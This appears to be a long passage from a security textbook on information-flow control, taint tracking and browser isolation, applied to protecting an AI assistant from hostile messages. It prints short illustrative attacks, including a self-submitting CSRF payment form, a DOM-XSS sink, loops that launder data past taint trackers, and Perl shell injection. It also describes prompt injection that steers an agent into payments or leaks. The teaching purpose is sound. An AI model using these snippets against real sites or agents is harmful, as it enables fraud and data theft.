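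The studies reach different conclusions partly because they count different things and examine different kinds of code. King and colleagues counted every violation of noninterference, however harmless, while Staicu and colleagues counted only problems that earlier research had shown to be exploitable. A login routine has to make a public decision that depends on a secret, so it necessarily contains implicit flows. A server module that runs an attacker's text as code has to receive that text, which is an explicit flow. An implicit flow might let the attacker decide whether the module runs some code, but not what that code contains.

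The methods also affect the results. JLift analyzed every path it could not rule out, including exceptions that could never occur, while the JavaScript monitor checked only the paths that the tests ran. Those tests covered both outcomes of every sensitive branch in just over half of the programs, so they may have missed some hidden flows.

Tracking explicit flows is therefore a reasonable way to find mistakes in honest programmers' code, and widely used taint trackers work this way. It protects less well against hostile programmers. The browser scripts needed more tracking partly because browsers already block many direct ways to read private data, so the scripts' authors used indirect ones. Staicu and colleagues expect attackers to turn to hidden flows where controls are strong.

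Agents are closer to the hostile case because a stranger's message can influence the programs an agent writes. Implicit flows also threaten integrity more directly in an agent than in a server module. If the assistant runs `if message contains "urgent" then pay(printer)`, the stranger controls whether Ana's money is sent, even though they can't choose the payee or the amount.

### A whole plan or one call at a time

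Some agents write a complete program before acting, as TACIT's agents do in Scala. Others choose each tool call after reading the result of the previous one.

A complete program can be checked statically. Smith distinguishes between using such checks to help honest programmers and to filter untrusted code. A model's plan falls in the second category, so the check has to work without a programmer's help and cannot automatically accept the plan's declassifications. But an agent's designer has two advantages over someone who checks downloaded software. The plan arrives as source code, and the designer can choose the language. A language without exceptions would avoid most of the false alarms that King and colleagues found. For example, Smith describes a proposal to skip an array write when the index is out of range, instead of raising an exception.

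The check happens before the assistant sends any mail or moves any money, so a rejected plan leaves nothing half done and the model can try again. However, the checker needs each input's sensitivity and trustworthiness in advance, as well as the right starting pc. If the model has read Ben's contract before writing the plan, the contract may have influenced every line, so the pc must start at Confidential and the checker will reject every public action in the plan. Static checking is therefore most useful when the model writes the plan from Ana's request alone.

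An agent that works step by step has no complete plan to check in advance. A monitor can inspect each call and use the actual labels of the data, but it can't observe a branch inside the model. If the assistant reads the contract and then requests a weather page, the monitor cannot determine whether the contract influenced that choice. The safe assumption, used in LIO, is that everything the model has read affects everything it does next. Under that assumption, a single read can cause the monitor to block later calls and leave Ana's task half finished.

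A designer can also combine the two methods. Buiras describes a version of LIO that lets programmers choose which checks to make before the program runs and which to make during execution. For Ana, a static check could confirm that the plan never tests an incoming message to decide whether to pay the printer. A monitor could then check the labels on messages as the plan fetches them, because their senders aren't known until then.

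## Enforcing labels between processes: Asbestos, HiStar and Flume

A monitor that can't observe a branch inside a program can still control what enters and leaves the program. Asbestos (2005), HiStar (2006) and Flume (2007), research systems from overlapping teams at MIT, Stanford and UCLA, did this in the operating system. They labeled files and processes (running programs that the operating system keeps apart) and checked the labels when data passed between them.

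Programmers can use this method without rewriting their software in a language such as Jif, but it is less precise. Everything inside a process shares one label, so if a mail program opens Ben's contract and then a newsletter, the system must treat all the program's later output as derived from both. The same holds for a language model because, according to *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025), nobody can yet trace labels through one precisely.

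### Asbestos: labels that spread with messages

In Asbestos, any process can create a compartment, for example for one user's private data. Each process has a send label, which records what it may have seen, and a receive label, which limits what it may accept. Both labels assign every compartment a level from 0 to 3. The default is 1 in send labels and 2 in receive labels. In simplified form, two rules apply when process P sends a message to process Q:

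- *Delivery check:* deliver the message only if send(P) ≤ receive(Q) in every compartment.
- *Contamination rule:* on delivery, send(Q) becomes send(Q) ⊕ send(P), which takes the higher level in each compartment.

Suppose Ana and Ben use terminals on the same computer, and a program that reads either user's files gets level 3 in that user's compartment. Ana's terminal has receive level 3 for her compartment and the default, 2, for Ben's. It accepts output from a program that has read only her files, but rejects output from one that has read Ben's, because that program's level 3 in Ben's compartment exceeds the terminal's receive level of 2.

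Data at level 3 can go only to processes that someone has cleared to receive it. Most processes can receive data at level 2, so a designer who uses that level lowers the receive labels of the few that must not receive it, such as the network service.

A fifth level, written ⋆, gives a process the right to release data from a compartment. Receiving messages does not contaminate the process in that compartment, and the process can pass the right on like a capability. To avoid confused deputies, Efstathopoulos and colleagues require a process that acts for several users to state which of its rights it is using for each write.

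Under the contamination rule, an ordinary web server that had handled requests from Ana and Ben would carry both their labels and could reply to neither. Giving the server the right to release everyone's data would solve this, but then one bug could expose all the data. A separate process for each user would be safe but would use a lot of memory.

Asbestos introduced event processes to avoid this choice. The server runs a loop that waits for a message and handles it. When a new user's first message arrives, the kernel creates an event process with its own labels and its own view of the server's memory. All event processes share the original memory, and the kernel copies only the pages that each one changes. When an event process finishes its work, the kernel keeps its labels and changed pages until that user's next message. An attacker who takes over Ana's event process therefore can't reach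 Ben's data.

In tests, each user's stored session took about 1.5 memory pages of 4 kilobytes, plus about eight more while the server handled a request. With one session, the server handled more requests per second than the Apache web server starting a new process for each request, but only a little over half as many as Apache running the same code inside its own processes, without isolation. At 10,000 sessions, its throughput fell to about half that of the slower Apache version. Each user added two entries to the labels of some trusted components, so these labels grew to more than 20,000 entries, and the kernel spent more and more time comparing them.

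The contamination rule also has the same flaw as the simple monitor in the four-line program, where an assignment that did not run revealed a secret. Krohn and Tromer, in *Noninterference for a Practical DIFC-Based Operating System*, show how a program could leak the bits 01 to a public accomplice. The accomplice starts two public helpers that can receive secret messages. To signal 0 and then 1, the program sends a message to the first helper and nothing to the second. The message raises the first helper's label, so that helper can no longer report to the accomplice. The second helper stays public and reports a 1 after a fixed wait. The accomplice takes the first helper's silence as a 0. Because creating an event process takes few resources, a program could use many helpers to leak thousands of bits per second.

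### HiStar and the untrusted virus scanner

HiStar prevents this attack by never raising a label automatically. A thread, the unit of execution within a process, must raise its own label before it can read secret data. Each helper would have to either stay public or raise its label in advance to be able to receive the message.

HiStar calls its compartments categories. Any thread can create one and then owns it, which the label shows as ⋆. For all other categories, a label gives one of four levels:

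| Level | Effect on an object with this level |
|---|---|
| 0 | ordinary threads may not modify it |
| 1 | no restriction (the default) |
| 2 | ordinary threads may read it, but not export what they read |
| 3 | ordinary threads may not read it |

A thread may read an object if the object's level is no higher than the thread's in every category the thread does not own. It may write to the object only if the levels are equal in all those categories, because a thread usually learns something about an object by writing to it. Each thread also has a clearance, the highest level to which it may raise itself. The default clearance is 2, so ordinary threads can't read data at level 3.

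Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and colleagues demonstrate these rules on ClamAV, an open-source virus scanner, in *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar*. A scanner has to read private files and process hostile ones. ClamAV has more than 40,000 lines of code, too many to check by hand before every urgent update. On Linux, an attacker who controlled the scanner could send a user's files over the network directly. The attacker could also leave them in a temporary directory for ClamAV's update program to send, or signal their contents to that program by locking parts of the virus database.

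On HiStar, a 110-line program called `wrap` starts the scanner. A user, Bob, owns two categories, r and w, which control who may read and write his files. `wrap` creates a third category, v, to isolate the scanner. In simplified form, the labels are:

| Component | r | w | v |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bob's files | 3 | 0 | 1 |
| `wrap` | ⋆ | 1 | ⋆ |
| Scanner and its helper programs | ⋆ | 1 | 3 |
| Scanner's private temporary directory | 3 | 1 | 3 |
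| Update program, virus database, network, Bob's terminal | 1 | 1 | 1 |

The scanner can read Bob's files, because it owns r and its levels in w and v are high enough. It can't change them, because its levels differ from theirs in both w and v. It can read the virus database but can't write to the database, the network or the terminal, which are all at level 1 in v. Any helper it starts has the same restrictions. The update program can use the network, but its clearance of 2 stops it from reading Bob's files or the scanner's temporary directory.

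Only `wrap` owns v, so only `wrap` can read the scanner's result and show it on Bob's terminal. Bob's privacy depends on the kernel and the 110 lines of `wrap`, even if an attacker replaces the scanner through a malicious update. The scanner could still signal through covert channels such as processor use, so `wrap` stops it after a set time.

The isolation did not measurably slow the scan:

| Task | HiStar | Linux | OpenBSD |
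|---|---|---|---|
| Scan a 100 MB file | 18.7 s | 18.7 s | 21.2 s |
| Scan the same file under `wrap` | 18.7 s | – | – |
| Download 100 MB | 9.1 s | 9.0 s | 9.0 s |
| Compile the HiStar kernel | 6.2 s | 4.7 s | 6.0 s |

Some individual operations were much slower than on Linux. Starting a program in the usual Unix way took 1.35 milliseconds on HiStar and 0.18 on Linux, because HiStar's Unix library made 317 kernel calls where Linux needed nine. A more direct method of starting the program cut HiStar's time to 0.47 milliseconds.

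### Flume: the same control on Linux

*Information Flow Control for Standard OS Abstractions*, by Krohn, Yip and colleagues, presents Flume, which was designed to provide these controls without a new operating system. Flume runs on Linux as an ordinary program and acts as a reference monitor. A small kernel module stops confined processes from making most system calls directly. They instead send their requests to Flume, which checks the labels and carries out the permitted ones.

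Flume replaces numbered levels with sets of tags. Each process p has a set S(p) of secrecy tags, for the kinds of secret it may have seen, and a set I(p) of integrity tags, for the guarantees that all its inputs meet. A process p without special rights may send to q only if

S(p) ⊆ S(q) and I(q) ⊆ I(p).

The network has no tags, so a process with any secrecy tag can't send to it. Each tag t has two rights, t⁺ to add the tag to a label and t⁻ to remove it. The process that creates t holds both and can give one of them to everyone. If everyone has t⁺, any program can read the tagged secrets, but only holders of t⁻ can release them. For integrity, the creator can instead give everyone t⁻ and keep t⁺, so only processes it trusts can certify data.

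A process with the right to release secrets could release them by accident whenever it writes. Flume therefore gives every open file, pipe and connection an endpoint with its own labels. Suppose Bob's command shell holds both rights for his tag b and starts an untrusted text editor labelled {b}. The shell gives the label {b} to its endpoints on the two pipes connecting it to the editor, and leaves its other endpoints public. Bob's secrets can then enter the shell only through a pipe that it has deliberately opened to them. If a program requests a forbidden endpoint label, Flume can report the error. Mistakes are harder to find in Asbestos, which silently drops forbidden messages because telling the sender could leak information.

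Krohn and colleagues tested Flume on MoinMoin, a wiki program with 91,000 lines of Python. MoinMoin checked permission to read pages in 41 places and permission to write in 19, and missing one check could expose a page. Under Flume, a small trusted program sets the labels for each request and then starts the wiki code as an untrusted process. The port changed about 1,000 lines and added another 1,000, together about 2% of the original's size.

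The ported code still contained two known flaws that had let users bypass MoinMoin's permissions, but they no longer revealed private pages. The port also exposed a previously undocumented leak. In the original, a user named Bob could find out whether a secret page called "ReasonsToFireBob" existed by trying to create a page with that name. Some harmless features, including search indexing and hit counters, stopped working because they moved data between users through shared files.

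The Flume version served 43% fewer page reads per second (18.8 instead of 33.2) and 34% fewer writes (11.1 instead of 16.9). Flume added 35 to 286 microseconds to most system calls, and a single page read required 753 calls to the monitor.

Krohn and Tromer later proved noninterference for a mathematical model of Flume, meaning that a process that has seen data with tag t and lacks t⁻ can't affect what an untagged process observes, except through a process that holds t⁻. The guarantee has a tiny chance of failing, because a program might guess a randomly chosen tag and use it to signal.

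They proved this by hand, and only for the model, so Flume's actual code may not match it. The model also leaves out timing and hardware such as the processor, memory and disk. The proof does show that Flume's rules lack the leak built into Asbestos's. In *Nickel*, Sigurbjarnarson, Nelson and colleagues went further by using an automated solver to verify noninterference for both the interface and the implementation of NiStar, a kernel inspired by HiStar.

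### What each design gained and gave up

| | Asbestos | HiStar | Flume |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted system code | kernel, about 28,000 lines | kernel, about 15,000 lines | about 21,500 lines plus all of Linux |
| Existing software | needs adapting to a new message interface | many Unix programs run with little or no change | Linux programs, with some system calls forbidden |
| Labels rise | automatically, on receipt | on request | on request |
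| Speed | half of Apache's at 10,000 sessions | close to Linux on two of three large tasks | 34–43% fewer wiki requests per second |

The figure for Asbestos follows from Zeldovich and colleagues' statement that HiStar's kernel has about 45% fewer lines of C. Applications add their own trusted code, such as `wrap` or the parts of the Asbestos web server that handle logins, connections and the database.

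HiStar offers the strongest protection of the three, with the smallest trusted base and no automatic label changes. Flume is easier to adopt because it benefits from Linux's drivers and updates, but any Linux flaw that gives an attacker administrator rights defeats it. Flume's approach is more realistic for a company that already runs its agents on Linux. Its slowdown would also matter less for agents, because a call to a language model usually takes far longer than the extra system calls.

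All three were research prototypes, and they mainly influenced later designs. Flume adopted HiStar's rule that processes must request label changes, and HiStar later adopted Flume's simpler labels. DStar extended the approach to networks of computers, and Loki moved part of HiStar's enforcement into hardware.

### A wrapper for Ben's contract

Ana's assistant can treat the language model as HiStar treats the scanner. A small trusted program, the wrapper, creates a tag for Ben's contract and keeps the right to remove it. It starts a worker that runs the model with that tag and whose only outside connection is a pipe to the wrapper. The worker reads the contract and Ben's questions and writes an answer, which the wrapper sends through the capability tied to Ben's thread. A second worker, which never sees the contract, reads the stranger's message and reports to Ana. Like event processes, the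 two workers run the same program but share no private state, so each must start with an empty context.

If the model runs on a provider's servers, the worker also needs a connection to them. Trusted code must then release the contract to the provider, and Ana and Ben have to trust the provider with it.

The dual-LLM pattern for agents is a similar arrangement. A privileged model has tools but never sees untrusted data, while a quarantined model reads untrusted data but has no tools. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) treats this as a special case of information-flow control and relaxes it by letting the quarantined model use tools, with labels restricting its calls after it has read untrusted data. Similarly, HiStar's scanner can start any helper program it needs to decode a file.

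The capability fixes where the answer goes, but the wrapper's code still has to be correct. The wrapper should have the right to remove only the contract's tag, so that it can't send out the result if a worker has also read the payroll. It should be ordinary code, because a language model in its place could follow instructions hidden in the worker's answer.

Ana's screen needs more care than Bob's terminal, because an image address in an answer could leak the contract, as in the SpAIware attack. The wrapper should therefore display answers as plain text.

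If Ben's questions quote the stranger's text, a false account number can still get into the answer, as it could with the reply capability alone.

Releasing anything to the public is even harder. The later magazine version of *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar* points out that `wrap` can't safely publish even one bit of the scanner's output, such as whether any file is infected, because a malicious scanner could use that bit to reveal anything about the user's data. Suppose the wrapper lets the worker decide whether to search the web for "penalty clause lawyer". An instruction hidden in Ben's questions could make that decision depend on whether the contract is worth more than €100,000, and the search company would receive the answer.

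## Tracking only direct data flows: taint tracking from Perl to browsers

Asbestos, HiStar and Flume give everything inside a process the same label. Taint tracking instead marks individual values, sometimes single characters, and follows the marks as a program copies and combines data, usually at run time. It tracks only explicit flows. Schoepe (2018), in *Flexible Information-Flow Control*, observes that taint tracking is more common in practice than methods that enforce noninterference, but that its guarantees are unclear.

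A taint policy specifies which sources produce marked data, such as incoming mail, and which sinks must refuse it, such as the account-number field of a payment tool. Its propagation rules specify which results inherit the marks of their inputs.

With T(x) for the set of marks on x, typical propagation rules are:

after `x := 5`, T(x) = ∅  
after `x := y`, T(x) = T(y)  
after `x := y + z`, T(x) = T(y) ∪ T(z)

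The union does the work of Denning's join, but nothing corresponds to the program-counter label. If a program copies an account number from the stranger's email into a payment, the mark reaches the sink and the tracker stops the payment. The following program gets past it:

```
payee := ""
for each digit d in message.account
    if d = "0" then payee := payee + "0"
    if d = "1" then payee := payee + "1"
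    ... and so on up to "9"
```

Every digit in `payee` is a constant from the program, so the tracker doesn't mark `payee`, even though it equals the stranger's number. A tracker that ignores implicit flows can therefore find bad flows but can't show that there are none.

Weak secrecy, one of the formal definitions in Schoepe's thesis, makes the remaining guarantee precise. The assignments and outputs that one run carried out, without the tests, form a straight-line program, which must satisfy noninterference. The example passes the corresponding test for integrity because its straight-line program only appends constants.

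### Perl's taint mode

Perl is a scripting language that many early websites used to process visitors' input. According to the Perl security manual, its taint mode marks command-line arguments, environment variables, all file input and the results of some system calls. The program stops with an error if it uses marked data in a command that starts a shell or changes files, directories or processes:

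```
$name = <STDIN>;            # tainted
open(F, "< $name");         # allowed: opens a file for reading
open(F, "> $name");         # refused: opens a file for writing
system("lookup $name");     # refused: runs a shell command
```

Without the last check, a visitor could type a semicolon followed by a second command, and the shell would run both.

Perl's taint checks have gaps. A program can print tainted data or use it to choose which function to call. Keys in a lookup table never carry taint. If an expression uses a tainted value to choose between two constants, the result is untainted, because Perl doesn't track this kind of implicit flow.

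Programs often need to use outside data after checking it. To clear the mark, a program matches the data against a regular expression, which is a pattern for text, and extracts the part in parentheses, which Perl calls `$1`:

```
if ($to =~ /^([-\@\w.]+)$/) { $to = $1; }   # checks, then clears
if ($to =~ /(.+)/)          { $to = $1; }   # clears without checking
```

The first pattern accepts only letters, digits, underscores, hyphens, at signs and dots, so it rejects the semicolon. The second accepts any characters on a line, yet Perl also marks its result as untainted. Perl's designers assumed that anyone who extracts text this way has thought about security. But programmers also use patterns just to split text, which clears the taint unintentionally.

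The manual says taint mode is meant to "prevent stupid mistakes, not to remove the need for thought". Taint mode assumes an honest programmer with untrustworthy users, and the manual recommends other protection for running a stranger's program. The checks slightly slow all Perl programs, including those that don't use them. Perl's *Configure option for not including taint support* proposes an easier way to build Perl without the checks. Under the initial plan, such a build would have rejected programs that request taint mode, but this would have stopped many Perl packages from installing.

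### Tracking machine instructions

Taint tracking can also protect programs whose source code is unavailable. In the early 2000s, internet worms such as CodeRed and Slammer took over servers by sending input that replaced an address stored in memory. When the server later jumped to the new address, it ran code the attacker had chosen. *Dynamic Taint Analysis for Automatic Detection, Analysis, and Signature Generation of Exploits* (Newsome and Song, 2005) introduced TaintCheck, a tool to detect such attacks.

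TaintCheck runs a program in an emulator and adds tracking code to every instruction that moves data or does arithmetic. Each byte of memory has a four-byte shadow entry, which, if the byte is tainted, points to a record of where the taint came from. By default, all data from the network is tainted. The sinks are format strings and the addresses the program jumps to. Format strings are templates for C's printing functions, and an attacker can use them to write to memory.

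Normal programs almost never take either from the network. TaintCheck detected every attack in the tests, including working exploits for three real servers. Under its default settings, it raised no false alarms on 15 programs, including a name server that processed 158,855 recorded queries.

It was also very slow. Compressing 15 megabytes of source code normally took 8.2 seconds. The emulator alone raised this to 25.6 seconds, and adding tracking raised it to 305 seconds, because nearly every instruction required several extra instructions to update the shadow memory. An early optimization reduced the slowdown from a factor of 37 to 24. Web requests slowed down less when the pages were large, because the server spent most of its time waiting for the network.

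TaintCheck also loses taint when a program uses tainted data to look up a value in a table. Microsoft's IIS web server, for example, converts each incoming character to another encoding this way. The result is a copy of a table entry, so TaintCheck doesn't mark it as tainted, even though the attacker chose which entry the server copied.

Other researchers responded with pointer tainting, which considers whether addresses are tainted. To detect spyware, they tainted any value that a program loaded from a tainted address, so that a typed character stayed tainted after a table lookup. To detect memory corruption, they raised an alarm whenever a program used a tainted address. Newsome and Song had considered this alarm and rejected it because programs routinely use input to choose an array element.

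In pointer tainting, if taint gets into a pointer to a large data structure, everything the program reads through that pointer becomes tainted too. Critics argued that such errors were inherent in pointer tainting and made it unsuitable for detecting spyware. *Tainting is not pointless* (2010) replied that many of their arguments did not apply to memory corruption. The critics, Slowinska and Bos (2010), maintained their objection to tainted pointers the same year in *Pointer Tainting Still Pointless*, but added in the subtitle that "we all see the point of tainting".

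The distinction between the two uses is reasonable. A spyware detector flags a program if marked keystrokes reach it, so stray marks anywhere in the system can make a harmless program look suspicious. A detector for memory corruption only has to check how a program uses addresses, though Newsome and Song's objection about arrays still applies to it.

### TaintDroid and 30 popular apps

Android lets a user decide whether an app may read her location, but not where the app may send it. In 2010 researchers introduced TaintDroid, a modified version of Android that logs when private data leaves the phone, which app sent it and where it went. *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert et al., 2014) describes an extended version of the system.

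TaintDroid avoids the cost of emulating a whole machine by tracking data at four levels:

| Level | What carries a mark | Typical error |
|---|---|---|
| Variable | each variable in an app's code | an array has one mark, so one private element taints the rest |
| Method | the result of a function in Android's built-in native libraries | the result may inherit marks from inputs it does not depend on |
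| Message | a whole message between apps | everything read from the message inherits all its marks |
| File | a whole file | everything read from the file inherits all its marks |

Each mark is a set of 32 bits, one for each kind of private data, such as location or phone number. Because TaintDroid tracks variables instead of memory addresses, it can taint the result of a table lookup with less risk of the mark spreading everywhere. It cannot monitor native code, which runs directly on the processor, so it blocks apps from loading the native libraries that come with them. Fewer than 5% of the popular free apps that the researchers scanned in 2010 included such a library.

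The original *TaintDroid* paper reported a 14% slowdown on a processor-intensive test. The 2014 version, which works with Android's newer just-in-time compiler, had a slowdown of up to 32%. Users would hardly notice either slowdown in an interactive app.

In April 2010 the researchers tested 30 popular apps that used location, camera or microphone data. Fifteen sent the user's location to advertising servers. Seven collected the phone's device ID, sometimes with the phone number and SIM card serial number. In total, 20 of the 30 used private data suspiciously. By September 2012 only 20 of the original apps were still available, and a similar proportion of them behaved suspiciously.

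These apps made no special effort to hide what they sent. An app that wanted to could have used a loop like this:

```
copy := 0
for i := 0 to 31
    if bit i of location = 1 then copy := copy + 2^i
send(copy)
```

TaintDroid ignores the test, and the additions involve only constants, so the app sends all 32 bits untainted. For small numbers, a shorter method is to create an array with that many elements and read its length, which TaintDroid never taints.

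Enck and colleagues acknowledge that apps can evade TaintDroid through implicit flows, but argue that doing so is itself evidence of malice, which static analysis might detect. This answer suits an app store, which has an app's code before anyone installs it. But an agent may write a program and run it seconds later, so the analysis would have to be automatic.

### Browsers that track characters

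Scripts on a web page often build new HTML or code out of text. If an attacker controls part of that text, their own script may run in a visitor's browser with the page's privileges. This attack is called DOM-based cross-site scripting when the fault lies in the page's own scripts. Here is an example adapted from slides by Stock, in *From Facepalm to Brain Bender*:

```
document.write("<img src='//ads.example/?tag=" + location.hash.slice(1) + "'/>")
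```

The source, `location.hash`, is the part of the page's address after the # sign, so an attacker can choose it by sending someone a link. If it begins with `'/>`, it closes the image tag, and the attacker can put a script after that.

Lekies, Stock and Johns (2013), in *25 Million Flows Later*, searched for these flaws with a modified version of Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome. They added one byte to each character of a string to record which of 14 sources the character came from, if any, and whether the page had applied any of three standard encoding functions to it. The browser reported any tainted string that reached a sink, such as `document.write` or `eval`.

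A report did not prove that an attack was possible, because the page might have made the text harmless first. A second program therefore used the marks to construct an attack for each suspicious flow. Each attack combined characters to break out of the surrounding text, a test script, and an ending that kept the leftover text from causing errors. The researchers counted a vulnerability only if the test script ran.

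| Stage | Number |
|---|---|
| Pages visited on the 5,000 most popular sites | 504,275 |
| Flows from a source to a sink | 24,474,306 |
| Flows with a working attack | 69,987 |
| Distinct vulnerabilities | 6,167 |
| Sites affected | 480 (9.6%) |

Fewer than three flows in 1,000 led to a working attack. The true number of vulnerabilities may be higher, since the program could miss attacks that a person would find. But blocking every tainted string at these sinks would have disrupted many harmless pages, so the tracker was more useful for deciding where to test.

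Later studies used the same combination of tracking and testing. *DEXTERJS* added the tracking code to web applications instead of the browser, and found 820 previously unknown vulnerabilities on 89 domains among the 1,000 most popular sites. In *Talking About My Generation* (2021), Bensalim, Klein and colleagues examined the top 100,000 sites for flows from a page's address into its HTML. They found 15,710 such flows and produced working attacks for 7,199 of them (46%), on 711 domains. This success rate was nearly double that of earlier methods.

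### Trusted Types

Trusted Types, a browser feature designed at Google and now a web standard, protects the same sinks without tracking any data. Chrome has supported it since 2020. When a site turns it on, sinks such as `innerHTML` and `eval` no longer accept ordinary strings. They accept only special objects, which a script must create through a named policy:

```
const policy = trustedTypes.createPolicy("mail", {
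    createHTML: text => sanitize(text)
});
box.innerHTML = policy.createHTML(message);   // accepted
box.innerHTML = message;                      // error
```

Taint tracking treats data as safe unless it is marked, so data that loses its mark passes the check. Trusted Types avoids this problem by requiring a policy to approve text before a sink accepts it. If a script copies a message one character at a time through branches, the result is still an ordinary string, and the sink rejects it. Reviewers can concentrate on the policies, and the site can list the policy names it allows.

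A careless policy is as harmful as a careless pattern in Perl. The policy `createHTML: text => text` approves everything, and the browser cannot detect that it checks nothing. Trusted Types also protects only the integrity of code and HTML, so it does not prevent a script from sending private data elsewhere.

### Too few marks or too many

Undertainting means that marks don't reach data that matters, as in the digit-copying program. Overtainting means that marks spread to so much data with little connection to the source that they no longer distinguish anything. Tracking every branch and table lookup reduces undertainting but increases overtainting.

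In 2021, Brant and colleagues reviewed 50 works on taint tracking and found that nearly all the systems followed only direct flows, partly to avoid overtainting and partly for speed. They argue that this is not always enough to protect integrity. Programs often convert, compress or decode input through branches and table lookups, and one earlier study found that trackers limited to direct flows missed many attacks that took control of a program. Some researchers have tried compromises, such as tracking only selected branches or giving indirect flows less weight, but Brant and colleagues consider the problem unsolved.

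Their survey also shows how much the cost depends on where the tracking happens:

| System | What does the tracking | Added running time |
|---|---|---|
| FAROS | software, for a whole machine | 5,600% |
| Dytan, which also follows branches | software, for one program | 3,000% |
| Panorama | software, for a whole machine | 2,000% |
| libdft | software, for one program | 114–603% |
| A processor design that also follows indirect flows | hardware and static analysis | 5–25% |
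| A processor design with four-bit tags | hardware | 1% |

The systems ran different tests, so only the large differences are meaningful. Hardware tracking is far faster, but it requires a modified processor and is harder to adapt to a new policy.

### Ana's sinks and the code that reaches them

Taint tracking has worked best on code that was buggy but not malicious and had few sinks. TaintCheck monitored ordinary servers for two dangerous uses of data, and the browser studies tested sites whose developers did not want them attacked. *Bochspwn Reloaded* used a simple tracker to find 30 flaws through which Windows exposed leftover memory contents to ordinary programs. TaintDroid is a partial exception in that it tracked untrusted apps, but it succeeded because their developers had not tried to evade it.

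Ana's assistant has only a few sinks, as long as every action goes through its own tools. Giving it a shell would make every command on her computer a sink too.

Taint tracking could catch mistakes in the tools and connecting program that the assistant's developers wrote, such as copying an account number from an email into a payment. But a program that the model writes after reading the stranger's message may contain the digit-copying loop, which taint tracking would miss. The model's output should carry the marks of everything the model has read, as it would in LIO.

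For payments, Ana's developers can borrow the design of Trusted Types. The payment tool would accept only a `Payee` object, and only the form where Ana types account numbers could create one. However a program copied the stranger's number, it would still be an ordinary string, so the tool would reject it. As with ScopeGate's list of permitted accounts, the stranger could still influence which approved payee the assistant pays.

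The same design is less useful for secrecy. A system could send outsiders only text that trusted code has approved as public. This would work for a fixed sentence such as "Your order has been sent", but not for a reply that the model writes after reading Ben's contract, because no simple check can establish that the reply reveals nothing about the contract.

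## Isolating by origin: the browser's same-origin policy and its successors

Trusted Types guards sinks inside a single web page. A browser also has to keep pages apart, since Ana may have her bank open in one tab and a stranger's website in another. It does this with the same-origin policy, which labels web content by the address it came from. Lukas, in *Same-Origin Policy (SOP)*, dates the policy to Netscape 2, a 1995 browser.

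An origin consists of a scheme (such as `https`), a host name and a port number. The path and anything after it are not part of the origin. According to http.dev's *Origins*, browsers drop the port if it is the scheme's default. Ana's bank page at `https://bank.example/accounts` therefore has the origin (https, bank.example, 443).

| Address | Same origin as the bank page? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
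| `https://bank.example/help?topic=7` | yes | only the path and query differ |
| `https://bank.example:443/accounts` | yes | 443 is the default port for `https` |
| `http://bank.example/accounts` | no | different scheme, and so a different default port |
| `https://pay.bank.example/accounts` | no | different host |
| `https://bank.example:8443/accounts` | no | different port |

A script can read or change another page only if the two pages have the same origin. It also can't read replies to requests it sends to other origins. W3C's *Same Origin Policy* notes that "there is no single same-origin policy", because the details differ between browser features. These variants are all meant to let people visit untrusted sites without those sites interfering with their sessions on honest ones.

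The policy still lets a page send requests to any origin and embed images, frames and scripts from anywhere. CS 161's *Same-Origin Policy*, a Berkeley course text, explains that embedded images and frames keep the origin they came from, so the surrounding page can read an image's dimensions but not its contents. An embedded script, however, runs with the origin of the page that includes it. If the bank loads a visitor counter from another company, that company's code can read Ana's balance.

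The same-origin policy resembles half of Bell-LaPadula. It restricts what a script may read, but hardly restricts where the script may send what it has read, since any script can put text into the address of an image it loads from another site.

### Requests that carry the user's authority

While Ana is logged in, her browser holds a cookie that identifies her to the bank, and traditionally it adds this cookie to every request to the bank, whichever page caused the request. A page on another site can exploit this with a form that submits itself:

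```
<form action="https://bank.example/transfer" method="POST">
  <input name="to" value="(the attacker's account)">
  <input name="amount" value="900">
</form>
<script>document.forms[0].submit()</script>
```

The bank receives a well-formed request with Ana's cookie and pays. The attacker's page can't read the bank's reply, but the attack works without it. This attack is called cross-site request forgery, and the browser is the confused deputy because it supplies Ana's authority for a request the attacker chose. The cookie is ambient authority in the same sense as the Tymshare compiler's licence.

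The usual defence is an unguessable token, which the bank puts in its payment form and expects back with each payment. The attacker's page can't read the bank's form, so it can't include the token. In effect, the bank stops relying on ambient authority and asks for something close to a capability. Reis, Moshchuk and Oskov (2019) name two other defences in *Site Isolation*. The browser can send the bank an `Origin` header that identifies where a request came from, or the bank can mark its cookie `SameSite`, so that the browser withholds it from requests that other sites initiate.

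### CORS: exceptions that the server grants

Sometimes a site wants another site to read its data. Suppose Ana's bookkeeping service at `https://books.example` needs her bank balance. Cross-origin resource sharing (CORS) lets the bank permit this. GRNET CERT, the security team of Greece's research network, describes the two headers involved. The browser states who is asking, and the server replies with the origins it allows, or with a wildcard for all of them:

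```
request:    Origin: https://books.example
response:   Access-Control-Allow-Origin: https://books.example
            Access-Control-Allow-Credentials: true
```

The browser gives the reply to the script only if the script's origin matches. The last line is necessary if the request carried Ana's cookie.

Before sending a request that an ordinary form could not produce, such as one that uses the DELETE method, the browser sends a "preflight" request to check whether the server accepts that method from that origin. This protects older servers, whose programmers assumed that other sites could not cause such requests. The browser sends no preflight for an ordinary form, so CORS does not prevent the forged payment.

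Browsers don't allow the wildcard with cookies, so developers who want to admit several sites sometimes copy the origin from each request into the reply. This check accepts every origin, just as a Perl pattern that matches everything accepts every input, so any page Ana visits can read her balance while she is logged in. Even a correct CORS rule doesn't control where the bookkeeping service sends the balance afterwards.

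### Content Security Policy and the trouble with lists of hosts

The same-origin policy does not stop cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets a script into the bank's own page, because the browser treats that script as having the bank's origin. Content Security Policy (CSP) is a second line of defence. The site sends a header listing where scripts may come from, for example `script-src 'self' https://cdn.example`, and the browser blocks all others.

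In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016) tested how well this worked by extracting 26,011 distinct policies from a Google index of about 106 billion pages and automatically checking each one for known ways around it.

| Policies | Number | Share an attacker could bypass |
|---|---|---|
| All distinct policies | 26,011 | 94.72% |
| Enforced policies that restrict scripts | 22,425 | 94.68% |
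| Those without obvious holes | 2,437 | 51.05% |

Of the policies that restricted scripts, 87.63% failed because they also contained `unsafe-inline` without a safeguard. This keyword allows scripts written directly into the page, where an attacker's script usually ends up. Sites used it because removing it meant rewriting much of their code.

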